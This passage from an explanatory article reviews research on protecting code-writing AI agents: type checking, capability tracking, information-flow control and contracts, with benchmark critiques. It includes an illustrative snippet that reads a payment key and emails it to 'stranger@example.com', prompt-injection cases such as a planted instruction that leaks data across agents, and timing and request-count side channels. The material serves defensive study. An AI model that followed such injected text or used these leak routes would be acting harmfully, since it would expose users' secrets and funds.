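orders = await find_orders(item="lamp", status="broken")
for order in orders:
    await issue_refund(order_id=order["id"], amount=order["price"])
```

Nobody can tell from this text how many refunds the program will issue or how large they will be. The host can still validate each call when the program makes it, but if the tenth call is malformed, nine payments will have gone out before the host rejects it.

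A type checker examines the program's text before any of it runs. It uses the declared types of the tools to work out the type of each expression, then checks that every value fits where the program uses it. If `find_orders` returns prices as text and `issue_refund` requires an integer, the checker rejects a program that passes one of those prices to `issue_refund`. This happens before any refund is paid, regardless of which orders the search would return.

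Which errors a check can find depends on the language and the method. *MuninAI* (2026), an agent framework for research groups, therefore labels each piece of generated code as executed, compiled or linted. A linter searches source code for common mistakes. Compiling C++ code also finds type errors, which linting R code misses. Running Python code finds errors that appear only during execution. A program can pass any of these checks and still compute the wrong result.

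### Filling a typed hole at runtime

*Generative Compilation* (2026) reports that many coding agents already run a compiler on a finished program and use the errors to revise the code. The paper's method runs the compiler while the model is still writing. A coding agent's user can usually review and test the program before relying on it, but an agent that writes a program to issue refunds runs it immediately and may never use it again.

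Zhao, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *LACUNA*, make the compiler part of the running agent. Their system, which they presented in May 2026, uses the idea of a typed hole, a placeholder in a program where the expected type is known but the code is missing. Earlier research used typed holes in code editors, where a programmer reviews what the model suggests. In LACUNA, the model fills the hole while the program is running. The hole is a function call in the programming language Scala:

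```scala
def agent[T](task: String): T
```

Here `task` is an instruction in plain language, and `T` is the type of result that the surrounding program needs. For example, `agent[Int]("count the broken lamps")` must produce an integer. The call proceeds as follows:

1. LACUNA sends the model the task, the type T, the surrounding source code with the hole marked, and a list of the available variables and their types.
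2. The model returns a snippet of Scala code.
3. LACUNA inserts the snippet into the surrounding source and runs the compiler on the result, with the same settings as for the original program.
4. If the compiler accepts the snippet, it runs inside the existing program, with access to the current values of the variables, and returns a value of type T.
5. If the compiler rejects the snippet, LACUNA adds the error messages to the prompt and asks the model again, up to a set number of attempts. After the last one, the call fails with an exception that the surrounding program can handle.

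The compiler checks the model's snippet by the same rules as a programmer's code. In one of the paper's examples, the surrounding program defines `tax` but not `price`. The model writes `price * (1.0 + tax)`, and the compiler reports that it cannot find `price`. The compiler would reject a call to an invented tool in the same way, because a tool in LACUNA is a function that the snippet can call. With optional settings for capability tracking, the compiler can also limit which effects a snippet may have.

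A snippet may contain further `agent` calls, which the model fills when execution reaches them. This lets an agent work in rounds, for example by searching, reading the results, and then calling `agent` again to decide what to do next.

The retry loop needs a limit because a model may repeat the same mistake. *MuninAI* stops after three attempts, or earlier if the same error recurs. It also does not let the model write tests for its own code, since the model could weaken them to pass. LACUNA's type check is similarly protected because the surrounding program sets T, although the model chooses the types of any nested calls it writes.

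### All or nothing

The compiler accepts or rejects a snippet as a whole. Zhao and colleagues illustrate this with a program that holds a balance of 100. The program calls `agent[Int]` with the task of subtracting 50 and returning the new balance, and the model writes:

```scala
balance -= 50
s"remaining: $balance"
```

The second line produces text, but the program needs an integer. The compiler rejects the snippet, so neither line runs. The balance is still 100, even though the subtraction came first and contained no error.

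An interpreter that does not check types beforehand can fail halfway. A similar mistake in Python would be:

```python
balance -= 50
"remaining: " + balance
```

Suppose the first line of a Python program subtracts 50 from a balance of 100, and the second line tries to join text to a number. Python runs the first line and then raises an error at the second, leaving the balance at 50. If the agent corrects the second line and reruns the whole program, the balance falls to 0. If the first line had issued a refund, the customer would have received it twice. This matters for the workflow in *From Tool Orchestration to Code Execution* (2026), where the agent writes and runs programs in a loop until one succeeds or it reaches a retry limit.

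LACUNA's guarantee covers only what happens before the snippet starts. Well-typed code can still divide by zero, run out of memory or lose its connection to a server. Suppose the compiler accepts the loop over broken lamps, but the shop's server stops responding during the fourth refund. The first three customers have been refunded, the fourth may or may not have been, and the rest have not.

Nested calls have the same limitation, because LACUNA compiles each snippet only when execution reaches it. If a snippet issues a refund and then calls `agent` to write a confirmation, the refund has already happened when the compiler checks the second snippet. If every attempt at the second snippet fails, the exception comes too late to prevent the refund. When an agent works in rounds, all-or-nothing rejection therefore covers only one round at a time.

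After a program fails at runtime, the model needs a record of the calls the program made. In Pydantic's system, the error message lists the calls that had started, their arguments, and whether each one returned. The list includes unfinished calls because a tool may have made its change before it stopped. However, nothing prevents the model from repeating these calls.

Some optional features give up all-or-nothing rejection for speed. Pydantic's eager mode runs each statement as soon as the model finishes writing it, so the first lines may take effect before an error in the last line is found. Its speculative mode starts selected tool calls early, even those in a branch the program never takes. It finds these calls by scanning the text, so it can start one that appears only in a comment. The developer can list the tools that are safe to call early or have the system rely on declarations such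 as MCP's `readOnlyHint`. If a server falsely set that hint on `issue_refund`, a sample call in a comment could issue a real refund.

### What the check cost in tests

Zhao and colleagues first tested the compiler without a model. They wrote about 400 cases that combined surrounding code with a snippet, some correct and some with mistakes that agents commonly make. The compiler handled all of them as expected.

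They then ran LACUNA on BrowseComp-Plus, a set of 830 difficult research questions about a fixed collection of roughly 100,000 documents. The agent could search the collection and open documents. With DeepSeek V4 Flash as the model, the compiler rejected 8.6% of the generated snippets. The agent averaged 0.7 retries per question, and two-thirds of the questions needed none. It answered 27.1% of the questions correctly.

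The team did not run the same agent without the check, so these results cannot support the paper's conclusion that type-checking "adds no accuracy cost". The results also provide little evidence about safety, because both tools only read documents, and a snippet that failed halfway would not have changed any of them.

The second benchmark, τ²-bench, consists of 392 customer-service tasks in which the agent talks to a simulated customer and uses tools to look up and change records. On this benchmark, a baseline agent used the same models and tools but made ordinary tool calls. The table shows the share of tasks solved.

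| Field | DeepSeek V4 Flash, tool calls | DeepSeek V4 Flash, LACUNA | Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, tool calls | Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, LACUNA |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Retail | 80.9% | 58.8% | 52.6% | 43.9% |
| Airline | 75.5% | 70.0% | 56.0% | 38.0% |
| Telecom | 100.0% | 88.6% | 15.8% | 14.9% |
| Telecom workflow | 95.4% | 83.3% | 21.1% | 24.6% |
| All tasks | 90.0% | 76.0% | 33.2% | 29.1% |

The paper describes LACUNA's 76.0% as "on par" with the baseline, but DeepSeek solved about 55 more tasks with ordinary tool calls than with LACUNA. The gap was widest in retail, the field most like the refund example, where the compiler rejected 22.4% of DeepSeek's snippets and the agent averaged 7.1 retries per task. The team ran each task only once, but a 14-point difference over 392 tasks is too large to plausibly be due to chance.

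It is unclear how much of this loss comes from type-checking, because one agent wrote programs and the other wrote single calls. Zhao and colleagues suspect Scala itself is part of the problem, because models have probably seen less of it in training than Python. A test with unchecked Scala, or with type-checked Python, would have helped separate these causes. Rejections alone do not predict the loss. The compiler rejected 89% of Gemini's snippets in the telecom tasks, but Gemini did almost as badly on those tasks with ordinary calls.

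Neither benchmark measured the main safety benefit. The paper reports how many snippets the compiler rejected, but not how many of them would have changed something before failing. If the error was in the first line, an interpreter would also have stopped before doing any damage.

Type-checking can be fast. Monty, Pydantic's Python interpreter for agents, took 4.8 milliseconds to run a one-line program with type-checking, about a thousand times as long as the 4.5 microseconds it took without. The added time is negligible next to a model call that takes seconds. Retries after a failed check add more time, since each one requires another model call.

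### Turning a new tool into a typed function

The compiler can check a call only if the tool already exists as a function with declared types. In the τ²-bench tests, each tool had a typed Scala function ready before the agent started. LACUNA let the model write new programs at runtime, but it did not show how an agent could use a tool it had just discovered.

A host can generate the missing interface from the tool's schema. For the refund tool, a Python version would look roughly like this:

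```python
async def issue_refund(*, order_id: str, amount: int) -> Any:
    """Issue a refund for an order"""
```

Cloudflare and Pydantic both generate such interfaces but use them differently. In Cloudflare's *How Code Mode works*, the model first writes a program that searches for a suitable tool and requests its types. It receives them as TypeScript declarations, which it uses as documentation when writing its next program. According to Cloudflare's *Codemode*, the system then parses the code and runs it as JavaScript. The listed steps don't include a type check. A program that passed "20 euros" as the refund amount would start running, and any earlier calls would take effect before the refund call failed.

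Pydantic also uses the generated interface for type checking. Monty checks the program against the declared types before running it, and any type errors go back to the model, which gets three retries by default. This comes closest to combining tool discovery with type checking, but it has gaps. If the host restores a session from an earlier run, the first program runs unchecked because the checker has no information about the variables already in the session.

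A generated interface may also contain less information than the schema. Python's `int` cannot express a minimum of 1, and `str` cannot express the pattern of an order number, so the host still has to validate each call. If the tool publishes no output schema, Pydantic declares its result as `Any`, so the type checker accepts any use of it. A program could then read `order["id"]` when the server names the field `order_id`, and the mistake would appear only at runtime.

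### When the schema is wrong

Shi and colleagues point out that a model relies implicitly on a tool's description matching its code. A type checker relies on the schema in the same way. Suppose the shop's schema gives `amount` as text, but the server accepts only integers. The checker will reject a program that passes 20 and accept one that passes "20". Its error messages will lead the model to replace the correct program with the wrong one, so more retries cannot help. The server will probably reject the resulting call, so no money will move.

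A wrong output schema can do more damage. Suppose a second tool reports whether the shop has already refunded an order. Its schema promises a true-or-false value, but the server returns the text "false". The agent writes:

```python
status = await refund_status(order_id="A-1043")
if not status["refunded"]:
    await issue_refund(order_id="A-1043", amount=20)
```

The program passes the type check. Python treats any non-empty text as true, so the program reads the text "false" as "already refunded" and skips the payment. The host could catch this by validating the result against the output schema before passing it to the program. That validation would not detect an incorrect Boolean `true` returned for an order that nobody had refunded.

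A generated interface can also carry the tool's prose description, including any hostile instructions in it. Pydantic advises developers to connect only to MCP servers they trust, because the text those servers supply becomes part of the agent's instructions.

### A type for euros

The original refund error passes the type check even when the schema is correct, because 20 and 2000 are both integers. A program can also repeat the error. The loop over broken lamps passes each price from `find_orders` directly to `issue_refund`, so if the prices are in cents, every customer receives a hundred times the right amount.

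To expose the error, a developer could give each unit its own type:

```scala
case class Euros(value: Int)
case class Cents(value: Int)

def issueRefund(orderId: String, amount: Euros): Receipt
```

If the model now writes `issueRefund("A-1043", 2000)`, the compiler reports an `Int` where it required `Euros`. This error message supplies the fact missing from the tool's description, so the model can correct the call to `Euros(20)`. In the loop, if each price has the type `Cents`, the compiler rejects the program until the model adds a conversion. *TypePilot* (Sternfeld, Kucharavy and Dolamic, 2025) cites a well-known case of such a mismatch. NASA lost its Mars Climate Orbiter in 1999 because one part of the system produced imperial units and another expected metric ones.

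However, the compiler would also accept `Euros(2000)`. The type protects best when the number comes from another typed tool rather than from a conversation, where the model has to label it itself. A type can also check its own values, as in one program in the TypePilot study, which defines an age type that accepts only values from 0 to 120. But that check runs when the program creates the value, which may be after other calls have taken effect.

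Models do not reliably write such types unprompted. Sternfeld and colleagues had three coding models write a Scala function that averages a list of ages. None of the functions handled negative ages correctly, even when the prompt asked for safe code that used the type system. When a second instance of each model listed the weaknesses and a third rewrote the code, two of the three functions handled negative ages correctly. The test was small, used older models, and did not involve agents calling tools.

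An interface generator that reads only `"type": "integer"` would not create a `Euros` type. The shop could state the unit in a custom `_meta` entry, and a generator built to read that entry could then create the type. A model could instead infer the unit from the tools' prose descriptions, but those may be false. If it relied on the customer's claim that refunds are in cents, it would declare `amount` as `Cents`. The compiler would then reject `Euros(20)` and accept `Cents(2000)`, and the shop would pay out 2,000 euros.

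## Limiting what the code may touch and where data may go

A program can pass every type check and still give away a secret. Suppose the shop keeps the key to its payment account in a file. The agent may read the shop's files and email its customers, and a line hidden in an order's delivery notes leads the model to write:

```scala
val key = readFile("secrets/payment-key.txt")
sendEmail("stranger@example.com", key)
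```

An agent can cause harm by passing a value from one permitted call to another, such as from `readFile` to `sendEmail`. The compiler finds no error because `readFile` returns text and `sendEmail` accepts text. Allowing or forbidding each tool separately would not prevent this either, because the agent needs both for its work.

Researchers have tried two ways to limit what an agent's code can do with data. One restricts what code can do while it handles a secret, and a compiler checks the restriction before the code runs. The other labels each value with its origin, and an interpreter checks the labels whenever the program calls a tool.

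### Capabilities and capture sets

In most programming languages, any line of code can open a file if it has the file's name. In a capability-safe language, the code also needs a capability, which is an unforgeable program value that grants a particular effect. For example, a function can write to a log file only if other code has given it the object for that file. The idea dates from operating-system research in the 1960s.

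Scala 3 has an experimental feature called capture checking that records capabilities in types. A type's capture set lists the capabilities that a value of that type may use. In this example, `out` is a capability for writing to a file:

```scala
val log     = (s: String) => out.write(s)   // type: String ->{out} Unit
val shorten = (s: String) => s.take(20)     // type: String -> String
```

The type of `log` shows that the function may use `out`. The compiler infers this capture set from the code and reports an error if the programmer declares a smaller one. The capture set of `shorten` is empty, so the function is pure. It can compute a result from its input but cannot write to a file, send a request or cause any other side effect. A capture set includes every capability the function uses and may include some it never uses.

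### Secrets in a wrapper

Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, use capture checking to control agents. TACIT, their system from EPFL, runs as an MCP server. The agent sends it Scala code in a tool call. TACIT compiles the code in a restricted "safe mode" and runs it only if the compiler accepts it. Safe mode forbids features such as unchecked type casts and reflection, which code could use to hide a capability from the compiler. The code can reach files, networks and other programs only through TACIT's own library.

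When the code reads a file from a directory that the user has designated as secret, it receives the content in a wrapper called `Classified`. A simplified definition is:

```scala
trait Classified[T]:
  def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

The `map` method applies a function to the hidden content and wraps the result again. The single arrow in `T -> U` means that `map` accepts only pure functions. The agent can therefore compute with the payment key but cannot send it anywhere:

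```scala
val key = readClassified("secrets/payment-key.txt")
key.map(k => k.length)                              // accepted
key.map(k => sendEmail("stranger@example.com", k))  // rejected
```

The compiler rejects the last line because sending an email requires a network capability, so the function is not pure. Passing `key` directly to `sendEmail` also fails because `Classified[String]` is not a `String`. If the agent prints the key, the model receives only `Classified(****)`, while the user can see the actual key on a separate channel.

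An agent often needs a language model to process secret text, for example to summarize a contract. TACIT can pass wrapped text to a second, trusted model that runs locally, and TACIT wraps that model's answer too. The model that wrote the code, which usually runs on another company's computers, never receives the contract or the summary.

File access works through a block of code:

```scala
requestFileSystem("/shop/orders") {
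  access("/shop/orders/A-1043.txt").read()
}
```

Inside the block, the code holds a capability for one directory, and the library rejects any path outside it. The block may return the text of the order, but not a file object or a function that could read more files later. The compiler rejects a program that returns either of these, because the value's type would have to refer to the capability, which does not exist outside the block. Similar blocks grant access to a list of websites or commands. In the published examples, the agent's own code chooses the directory and the websites, so these blocks restrict a hostile agent only if the library or the host refuses requests that are too broad.

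The protection relies on the Scala compiler, TACIT's library, the software that runs the compiled code, and any local model, but not on the cloud model, which the design assumes may be hostile. Researchers have machine-checked proofs for the core of capture checking, but not yet for safe mode. A programmer can also mark library code as safe by hand, and a mistake there could leak secrets. Someone also has to keep the secrets in the designated directories. If an employee pastes the payment key into an ordinary order file, the agent receives it as plain text.

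### Tests of TACIT

To test for leaks, Odersky and colleagues used a small software project with a directory of access keys, a database and confidential documents. They ran Claude Sonnet 4.6 and MiniMax M2.5 each through 131 trials twice, once with the wrapper and once with the secrets as ordinary text. For 120 of the trials, they paired each of 12 legitimate tasks with each of 10 injected texts, such as fake error messages and ready-made Scala code for reading the secrets. In the other 11, the user asked for secrets outright or falsely claimed authority to see them. The table shows the share of trials in which no secret appeared in the agent's output.

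| Trials | Sonnet, wrapper | Sonnet, no wrapper | MiniMax, wrapper | MiniMax, no wrapper |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Legitimate task with injected text (120) | 100% | 100% | 100% | 97.5% |
| Malicious request (11) | 100% | 81.8% | 100% | 27.3% |
| All (131) | 100% | 98.5% | 100% | 91.6% |

Without the wrapper, the two models leaked secrets in 13 trials, 10 involving malicious requests and three involving injections. All three injections were against MiniMax, so the wrapper had few injection attacks to stop. The perfect scores are expected from the design, since the model never receives the secrets. All the attacks the paper describes tried to persuade the model. None exploited a bug in the compiler or the library, where the protection would be most likely to fail.

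The wrapper did not make the agents less useful in this test. Sonnet completed 99.2% of the legitimate tasks with the wrapper and 83.3% without, and MiniMax completed 90.0% with it and 88.3% without. Odersky and colleagues suspect that Sonnet's gain is an artefact of the set-up. Without the wrapper, Sonnet often ran out of time or turns, and it sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection.

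On τ²-bench, the customer-service benchmark, all three models scored slightly higher with TACIT than with ordinary tool calls. The gains ranged from 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points across the airline and retail tasks, with ten runs per task. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software faults, MiniMax repaired 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% with ordinary tools. LACUNA, which also has the model write Scala, did worse than tool calls on τ²-bench. TACIT's results suggest that Scala alone does not explain LACUNA's lower scores, although the two studies used different models and set-ups.

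The τ²-bench functions in TACIT returned customers' orders as ordinary values, which the agent could read. The comparison therefore measures how writing typed Scala affects the agent's performance, but doesn't test the added difficulty of working with data the agent cannot read.

### Injection through tool results

TACIT's wrapper prevents secrets from leaking, but it does not block hostile instructions. If a delivery note is not in a secret directory, the agent reads it as plain text, and instructions in the note may lead the agent to issue a refund. The compiler will accept that refund like any other. The survey *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026) notes that "unsafe behavior can arise from influence, not content alone". For example, the number 2000 is harmless in itself, but it may be unsafe as a refund amount if a customer was able to choose it.

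Information-flow control sets rules on where data may go, based on its source or how secret it is. The best-known version for agents is CaMeL, which Google DeepMind presented in 2025. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) describes CaMeL's design. One model, the planner, reads the user's request and writes a program in a restricted form of Python before any tool runs. A second, "quarantined" model reads untrusted text but has no tools. An interpreter executes the program, calls the tools and stores their results in variables.

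Suppose the user asks the agent to refund order A-1043 for whatever the customer's note gives as the price of the lamp. The planner could write the following program, in which `ask_reader` calls the quarantined model:

```python
order = find_order("A-1043")
price = ask_reader("What did the lamp cost?", order["notes"], int)
issue_refund(order_id="A-1043", amount=price)
```

If the note contains an instruction to refund every purchase since January, the quarantined model may follow it but can only return an integer. The program still issues one refund on one order. The planner never reads the note, so the note cannot make it write another call.

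The customer can still influence the amount. A note that puts the price at 2,000 euros may lead the quarantined model to return 2000. The interpreter therefore tags each value with its sources and who may read it. (CaMeL calls these tags capabilities, but unlike TACIT's capabilities, they describe data and do not themselves grant an effect.) Before each call, a policy, written as a short Python function, checks the arguments and their tags and allows or denies the call. The shop's policy could deny any refund whose amount comes from a customer's text. It would also deny such refunds when the customer is honest, so the planner would have to take the price from the shop's records instead.

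### Results on AgentDojo

Researchers usually test such defences on AgentDojo, which simulates office work, banking, travel booking and the messaging service Slack. The original version, from *AgentDojo* (2024), has 97 tasks and 629 security tests, each of which combines a task with an attack. The attacker's text appears where text from outsiders normally would, such as in the body of an email. According to *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026), a program checks the final state, for example whether money has moved, so no language model has to judge the outcome.

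*SecureClaw* (2026), which presents a rival system, reports a test of CaMeL on this version. None of the 629 attacks succeeded, but CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 tasks without an attack and 195 of the 629 with one. SecureClaw completed 59 and 356 respectively. The SecureClaw team had to adapt CaMeL's published code, and someone with more knowledge of CaMeL might have got better results.

Odersky and colleagues ran TACIT on a larger version of AgentDojo and compared the results with those in the original CaMeL paper. The table shows the share of tasks completed.

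| Field | Gemini 2.5 Pro, CaMeL | Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT | o4-mini, CaMeL | o4-mini, TACIT |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 52.8% | 56.9% | 62.5% | 59.0% |
| Office work | 53.8% | 50.5% | 81.4% | 52.9% |
| Slack | 48.6% | 40.0% | 68.6% | 47.6% |
| Travel | 1.4% | 64.3% | 74.3% | 68.6% |

The paper calls these results comparable, but with o4-mini, TACIT's completion rate was 28 percentage points lower on the office tasks and 21 points lower on the Slack tasks. CaMeL's own results also vary widely by model, from almost no travel tasks completed with Gemini to three-quarters with o4-mini.

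Each system let through one attack in 1,926 trials. In TACIT's case, the attacker had added a recommendation for another hotel to the reviews of the one the user wanted. The agent booked the right hotel and took no harmful action, but it quoted the reviews in its answer, and the benchmark counted the mention of the other hotel as a success for the attacker.

For this test, the team wrapped the emails, files and web pages in `Classified`, so the agent could not read the attacks in them. A separate model processed the text inside `map`. However, the banking function `sendMoney` did not require a capability, and according to the agent's instructions, side effects inside `map` take place immediately. A program could therefore apparently send a payment from inside `map`, which the purity rule is supposed to prevent. If so, the low attack rate is mainly due to keeping hostile text away from the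 agent, as CaMeL does, rather than to capture checking.

Attacks on this benchmark rarely succeed against newer models, even without these defences. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, split AgentDojo's tools among several cooperating agents and ran 949 attacks per model. Without CaMeL, 36.1% of the attacks succeeded against GPT-4.1 and 24.6% against Gemini 2.5 Pro, but only 1.5% succeeded against Claude Fable 5 and none against GPT-5.5. Peters-Gill and colleagues warn that this does not show GPT-5.5 is immune, because attackers who adapt their texts to the model have succeeded against every frontier model in a large test.

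Strong models also complete fewer tasks with CaMeL. On AssetOpsBench, a benchmark of professional tasks for cooperating agents, CaMeL reduced the completion rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points across five models, and by an average of 13.4 points for the two strongest, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5.

### Letting the planner read

Some of the lost tasks are impossible under CaMeL's design. If a user asks the agent to do whatever is due today on a to-do list, the planner cannot write the program in advance, because the necessary calls depend on what the list contains.

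FIDES, a system from Microsoft, relaxes the separation. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, let the planner work step by step, as an ordinary agent does. FIDES keeps untrusted results in variables, and the planner can either ask a quarantined model about them or open them and read the text itself. Every value has a label for trust and a label for secrecy. When the agent derives a value from two others, the system combines their labels with an operation called a join (⊔):

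```
trusted ⊔ untrusted = untrusted
{Ana, Ben, Cem} ⊔ {Ben, Cem, Dora} = {Ben, Cem}
```

The second line combines lists of authorized readers. Only Ben and Cem may read both originals, so only they may read a text based on both.

The same rule applies to the planner's context, the text it has read so far. Once the planner opens an untrusted variable, the whole context becomes untrusted, and so does every call it writes afterwards. A policy can then block payments and other consequential calls. The planner may send data out as long as every recipient is authorized to read it. FIDES stopped every attack in AgentDojo when these policies were enforced. Some attacks succeeded against every planner that Costa and colleagues tested without them, including FIDES.

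*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) presents PRUDENTIA, a system built on FIDES. In FIDES, the planner is not given the policies, so it may open a variable too early and have its next call blocked. PRUDENTIA gives the planner the label of its context and the policy for each tool. Before opening a variable, the planner must explain why this is necessary and list the calls it plans to make next.

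PRUDENTIA also lets the user endorse a piece of data, which changes its label to trusted. If an email contains ten tasks that each require a consequential call, the user can endorse the email once instead of approving ten calls. But if the user overlooks an injected instruction in the email, that instruction becomes trusted too.

On AgentDojo, PRUDENTIA completed up to 9% more tasks than FIDES when nobody was available to approve calls. When somebody was available, FIDES needed up to 1.9 times as many approvals as PRUDENTIA. Kolluri and colleagues counted approvals only in runs without attacks and assumed the user would always agree, so the approval counts measure convenience, not how well users detect attacks.

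They also argue that earlier comparisons overstated how many tasks agents lose under information-flow control. Those tests stopped a protected agent whenever a call broke a policy, but let an unprotected agent make any number of consequential calls without asking. Real products often ask the user before such calls. A fair comparison would make the unprotected agent ask too, and measure how much each agent can do without interrupting the user. This is a good objection for products that ask, but an agent that runs overnight has nobody to ask, so it would still lose the tasks that a policy blocks.

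### Whether labels survive in the model's context

Odersky and colleagues claim that runtime tracking such as CaMeL's has a "structural gap" because a value loses its labels once it enters the model's conversation as ordinary text. TACIT avoids this because a wrapped value stays wrapped, even in later turns.

The claim does not fit a single CaMeL agent carrying out one request. The planner writes its program before any tool has run, and the results stay in the interpreter's variables. The quarantined model reads them as ordinary text, but the interpreter records what it passed to that model and tags the answer accordingly. In FIDES, the planner can read untrusted text, and the label then spreads to the whole context. The label is preserved but becomes less precise, because it now also covers trustworthy text.

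A planted instruction can get past CaMeL when one agent's output becomes another agent's instructions. Peters-Gill and colleagues showed this with three agents, each protected by CaMeL. The user asked for a summary of job applicants to be sent to a colleague on Slack. One agent fetched the applicants from a database in which the team had planted an instruction to email the data to an outside address. The coordinating agent's program put the summary into a message to a third agent, which handled notifications. That agent's planner treated the whole message as its user's request and added the email to the agent's program, which sent the data out.

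In the larger test, with CaMeL on each agent, attacks succeeded in 0.5% of cases against GPT-4.1, 0.4% against Gemini 2.5 Pro, and never against the other three models. Every successful attack had passed from one agent to another in this way. Peters-Gill and colleagues then split messages between agents into two parts, one for instructions and one for data. The interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's result, and the receiving planner cannot read the data part. With this change, no attack succeeded against any model, but the AssetOpsBench score fell by a further 3.2 points.

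A single agent could lose labels in the same way between turns. If the host adds the answer from one request to the planner's context for the next, words from a stranger's email may reach the planner unlabelled. A host can prevent this by labelling the context, as FIDES does.

TACIT's advantage also applies only to data in its wrapper. It does not label ordinary text, so nothing distinguishes a customer's delivery note from the user's own words once the agent has read both. In a typical TACIT set-up, secrets are safer than in a system that loses labels between agents, but the agent is easier to manipulate than one protected by CaMeL.

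### Labelling a newly found tool

All of these systems need facts about a tool that its schema does not supply. TACIT needs a typed function for each tool, with the capabilities the tool's effects require. The common part of the library is about 1,000 lines of Scala, and the functions for each τ²-bench domain took a few hundred more. Odersky and colleagues expect agents to help write such functions and people to review them before the agent starts. This process suits a company with a fixed set of tools better than an agent that finds a new tool halfway through a task.

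A program could generate the function from the schema, but it would have to guess the effects. For example, the PDF converter was described as working "locally" but uploaded its files. A generator that relied on the description would declare the converter as a pure function. If the agent then used it inside `map` on a secret contract, the compiler would accept the program and the tool would upload the contract. To be safe, the generator could require a network capability for every tool on a remote server, but then the agent could not use any of those tools inside `map`.

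CaMeL needs a policy for each tool. In *Operationalizing CaMeL*, Tallam and Miller (2025) warn that an organization with hundreds of tools would end up with duplicate and inconsistent policies. CaMeL also needs to know the format of a tool's results in advance, because the planner writes the code that processes them without having seen any. Peters-Gill and colleagues had to add this information to every tool description in their benchmarks.

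For an unknown tool, a host could treat every result as untrusted and every call as consequential. This would avoid labeling the tool too permissively, but the agent would have to ask the user more often or leave more tasks unfinished.

But cautious labels on results do not protect against a poisoned tool description. CaMeL's planner reads the tools' descriptions along with the user's request, and Costa and colleagues explicitly assume that the descriptions are trustworthy. Suppose the customer's exchange-rate tool again comes with the false claim that the shop's refunds are in cents. The planner reads the claim before it writes the program, so it writes `amount=2000` itself. The interpreter treats that number as trusted, and a policy that blocks amounts from customers lets it through.

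### Side channels and external commands

Data can also leave a program indirectly. TACIT prevents code inside `map` from sending the payment key, but not from taking longer when the first bit of the key is 1. An agent that measures the time learns that bit and could learn the others the same way. Odersky and colleagues exclude timing from their guarantee.

Tallam and Miller describe a similar leak in CaMeL, in which a program reveals a secret number by requesting a harmless web page that many times. No request contains the secret, but anyone who can read the web server's log can count the requests. TACIT blocks this version because a function that sends web requests is not pure.

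External commands are a larger gap because TACIT lets code run programs from an approved list, but the compiler cannot check what those programs do. Odersky and colleagues recommend a short list of safe commands and give `git diff` and `sbt` as examples. But `sbt` is a build tool that runs code from a project's build files, so an agent that can edit those files could use it to run almost anything. Operating-system isolation then has to limit the damage.

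### Wrong but authorized actions

An attacker may succeed without breaking any rule. CaMeL fixes the possible calls in advance, but data can still determine which of them the program makes. If the planner writes a program that refunds the customer whenever the note reports a broken lamp, a dishonest customer can get a refund by falsely reporting one. The program then does what the user asked for, and a stricter policy that blocked this refund would also block refunds to honest customers.

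The original refund mistake does not involve an attacker or a secret. TACIT's `sendMoney` function takes the amount as a plain number, and TACIT is explicitly not designed to prevent logical errors. In CaMeL, the planner can make the same mistake and write 2000 into the program. Since no untrusted data influenced the number, it gets the most trusted label, and a policy that blocks untrusted amounts allows the payment.

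## Preconditions, postconditions and rules on the order of calls

A program could catch the 2,000-euro refund by looking up the order and comparing the refund with the order's price. None of the checks described so far does this. A contract can include this comparison because it states what must be true of the shop's records before a call and what must be true afterwards.

### A contract for the refund

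The usual notation is the Hoare triple, which the computer scientist Tony Hoare introduced in 1969:

```
{P} t {Q}
```

If the precondition P holds before the program t runs, the postcondition Q must hold when t finishes. If P is false before t runs, there is no guarantee about what t does. *Talk is Cheap, Logic is Hard* (2026) gives the example of a function that finds the largest number in a list. The precondition is that the list is not empty, and the postcondition is that the result is in the list and no number in the list is larger.

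The shop could write this contract for its refund tool:

```
P:  order_id exists
    refunded(order_id) = 0 euros
    0 < amount <= total(order_id), both in euros

t:  issue_refund(order_id, amount)

Q:  refunded(order_id) = amount euros
    no other order has changed
```

The server or the host enforces P by evaluating it with the actual values just before the call. Order A-1043 cost 20 euros, so the condition 2000 <= 20 is false and the payment does not go out. The error message can include the limit, so the model has a good chance of sending 20 next time. The second line of P blocks a repeated refund. A 2,000-euro refund for the sofa passes, because the limit now depends on the order.

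The contract catches the confusion of euros and cents only if the wrong amount exceeds the price of the order, so it misses a hundredfold error when the correct refund is at most 1% of the price. If the customer should get 3 euros back on the 2,000-euro sofa and the agent sends 300, every line of P holds. The contract also depends on its author knowing the tool's unit. An author who believed that the tool took cents would write a check that treats 2000 as 20 euros, and for an order priced at 20 euros that check would allow the payment.

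Where the check runs also matters. If two agents handle the same order at once, both may evaluate P before either has paid, and the customer gets two refunds. The server can prevent this by checking and paying in a single database transaction, which a host that checks from outside cannot do.

*When Code Becomes an LLM Call* (2026), a study of contracts around model calls, distinguishes three levels of assurance. A "prompt-only" constraint is an instruction to the model that no program verifies, such as a request never to refund more than the price. A "code-checked" constraint is one a program tests, like P above. A "capability-bound" constraint is one the model has no means of breaking. For example, the shop could replace its tool with `refund_in_full(order_id)` and let the server look up the price. This would prevent the model from writing 2000, but also from giving a partial refund.

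### ToolGate

Liu, Peng and colleagues (2026), in *ToolGate*, made contracts part of how an agent chooses its tools. Their system, from January 2026, keeps a "symbolic state", a list of facts that it treats as established. Each fact has a key, a value and a type. For the refund, the state might contain:

```
order_id     = "A-1043"  : OrderNumber
order_total  = 20        : Euros
refunded     = false     : Boolean
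```

A tool call then proceeds as follows:

1. The model signals that it needs a tool and describes what for.
2. An embedding model retrieves the ten closest tools, and a second small model ranks them by giving each a probability.
3. The host removes every tool whose precondition is false in the current state.
4. It rescales the remaining probabilities so that they add up to 1, and picks a tool.
5. The system fills in the arguments and executes the call.
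6. The host checks the result against the postcondition. If the result passes, the host adds it to the state and shows it to the model. Otherwise, the host discards the result and leaves the state as it was.

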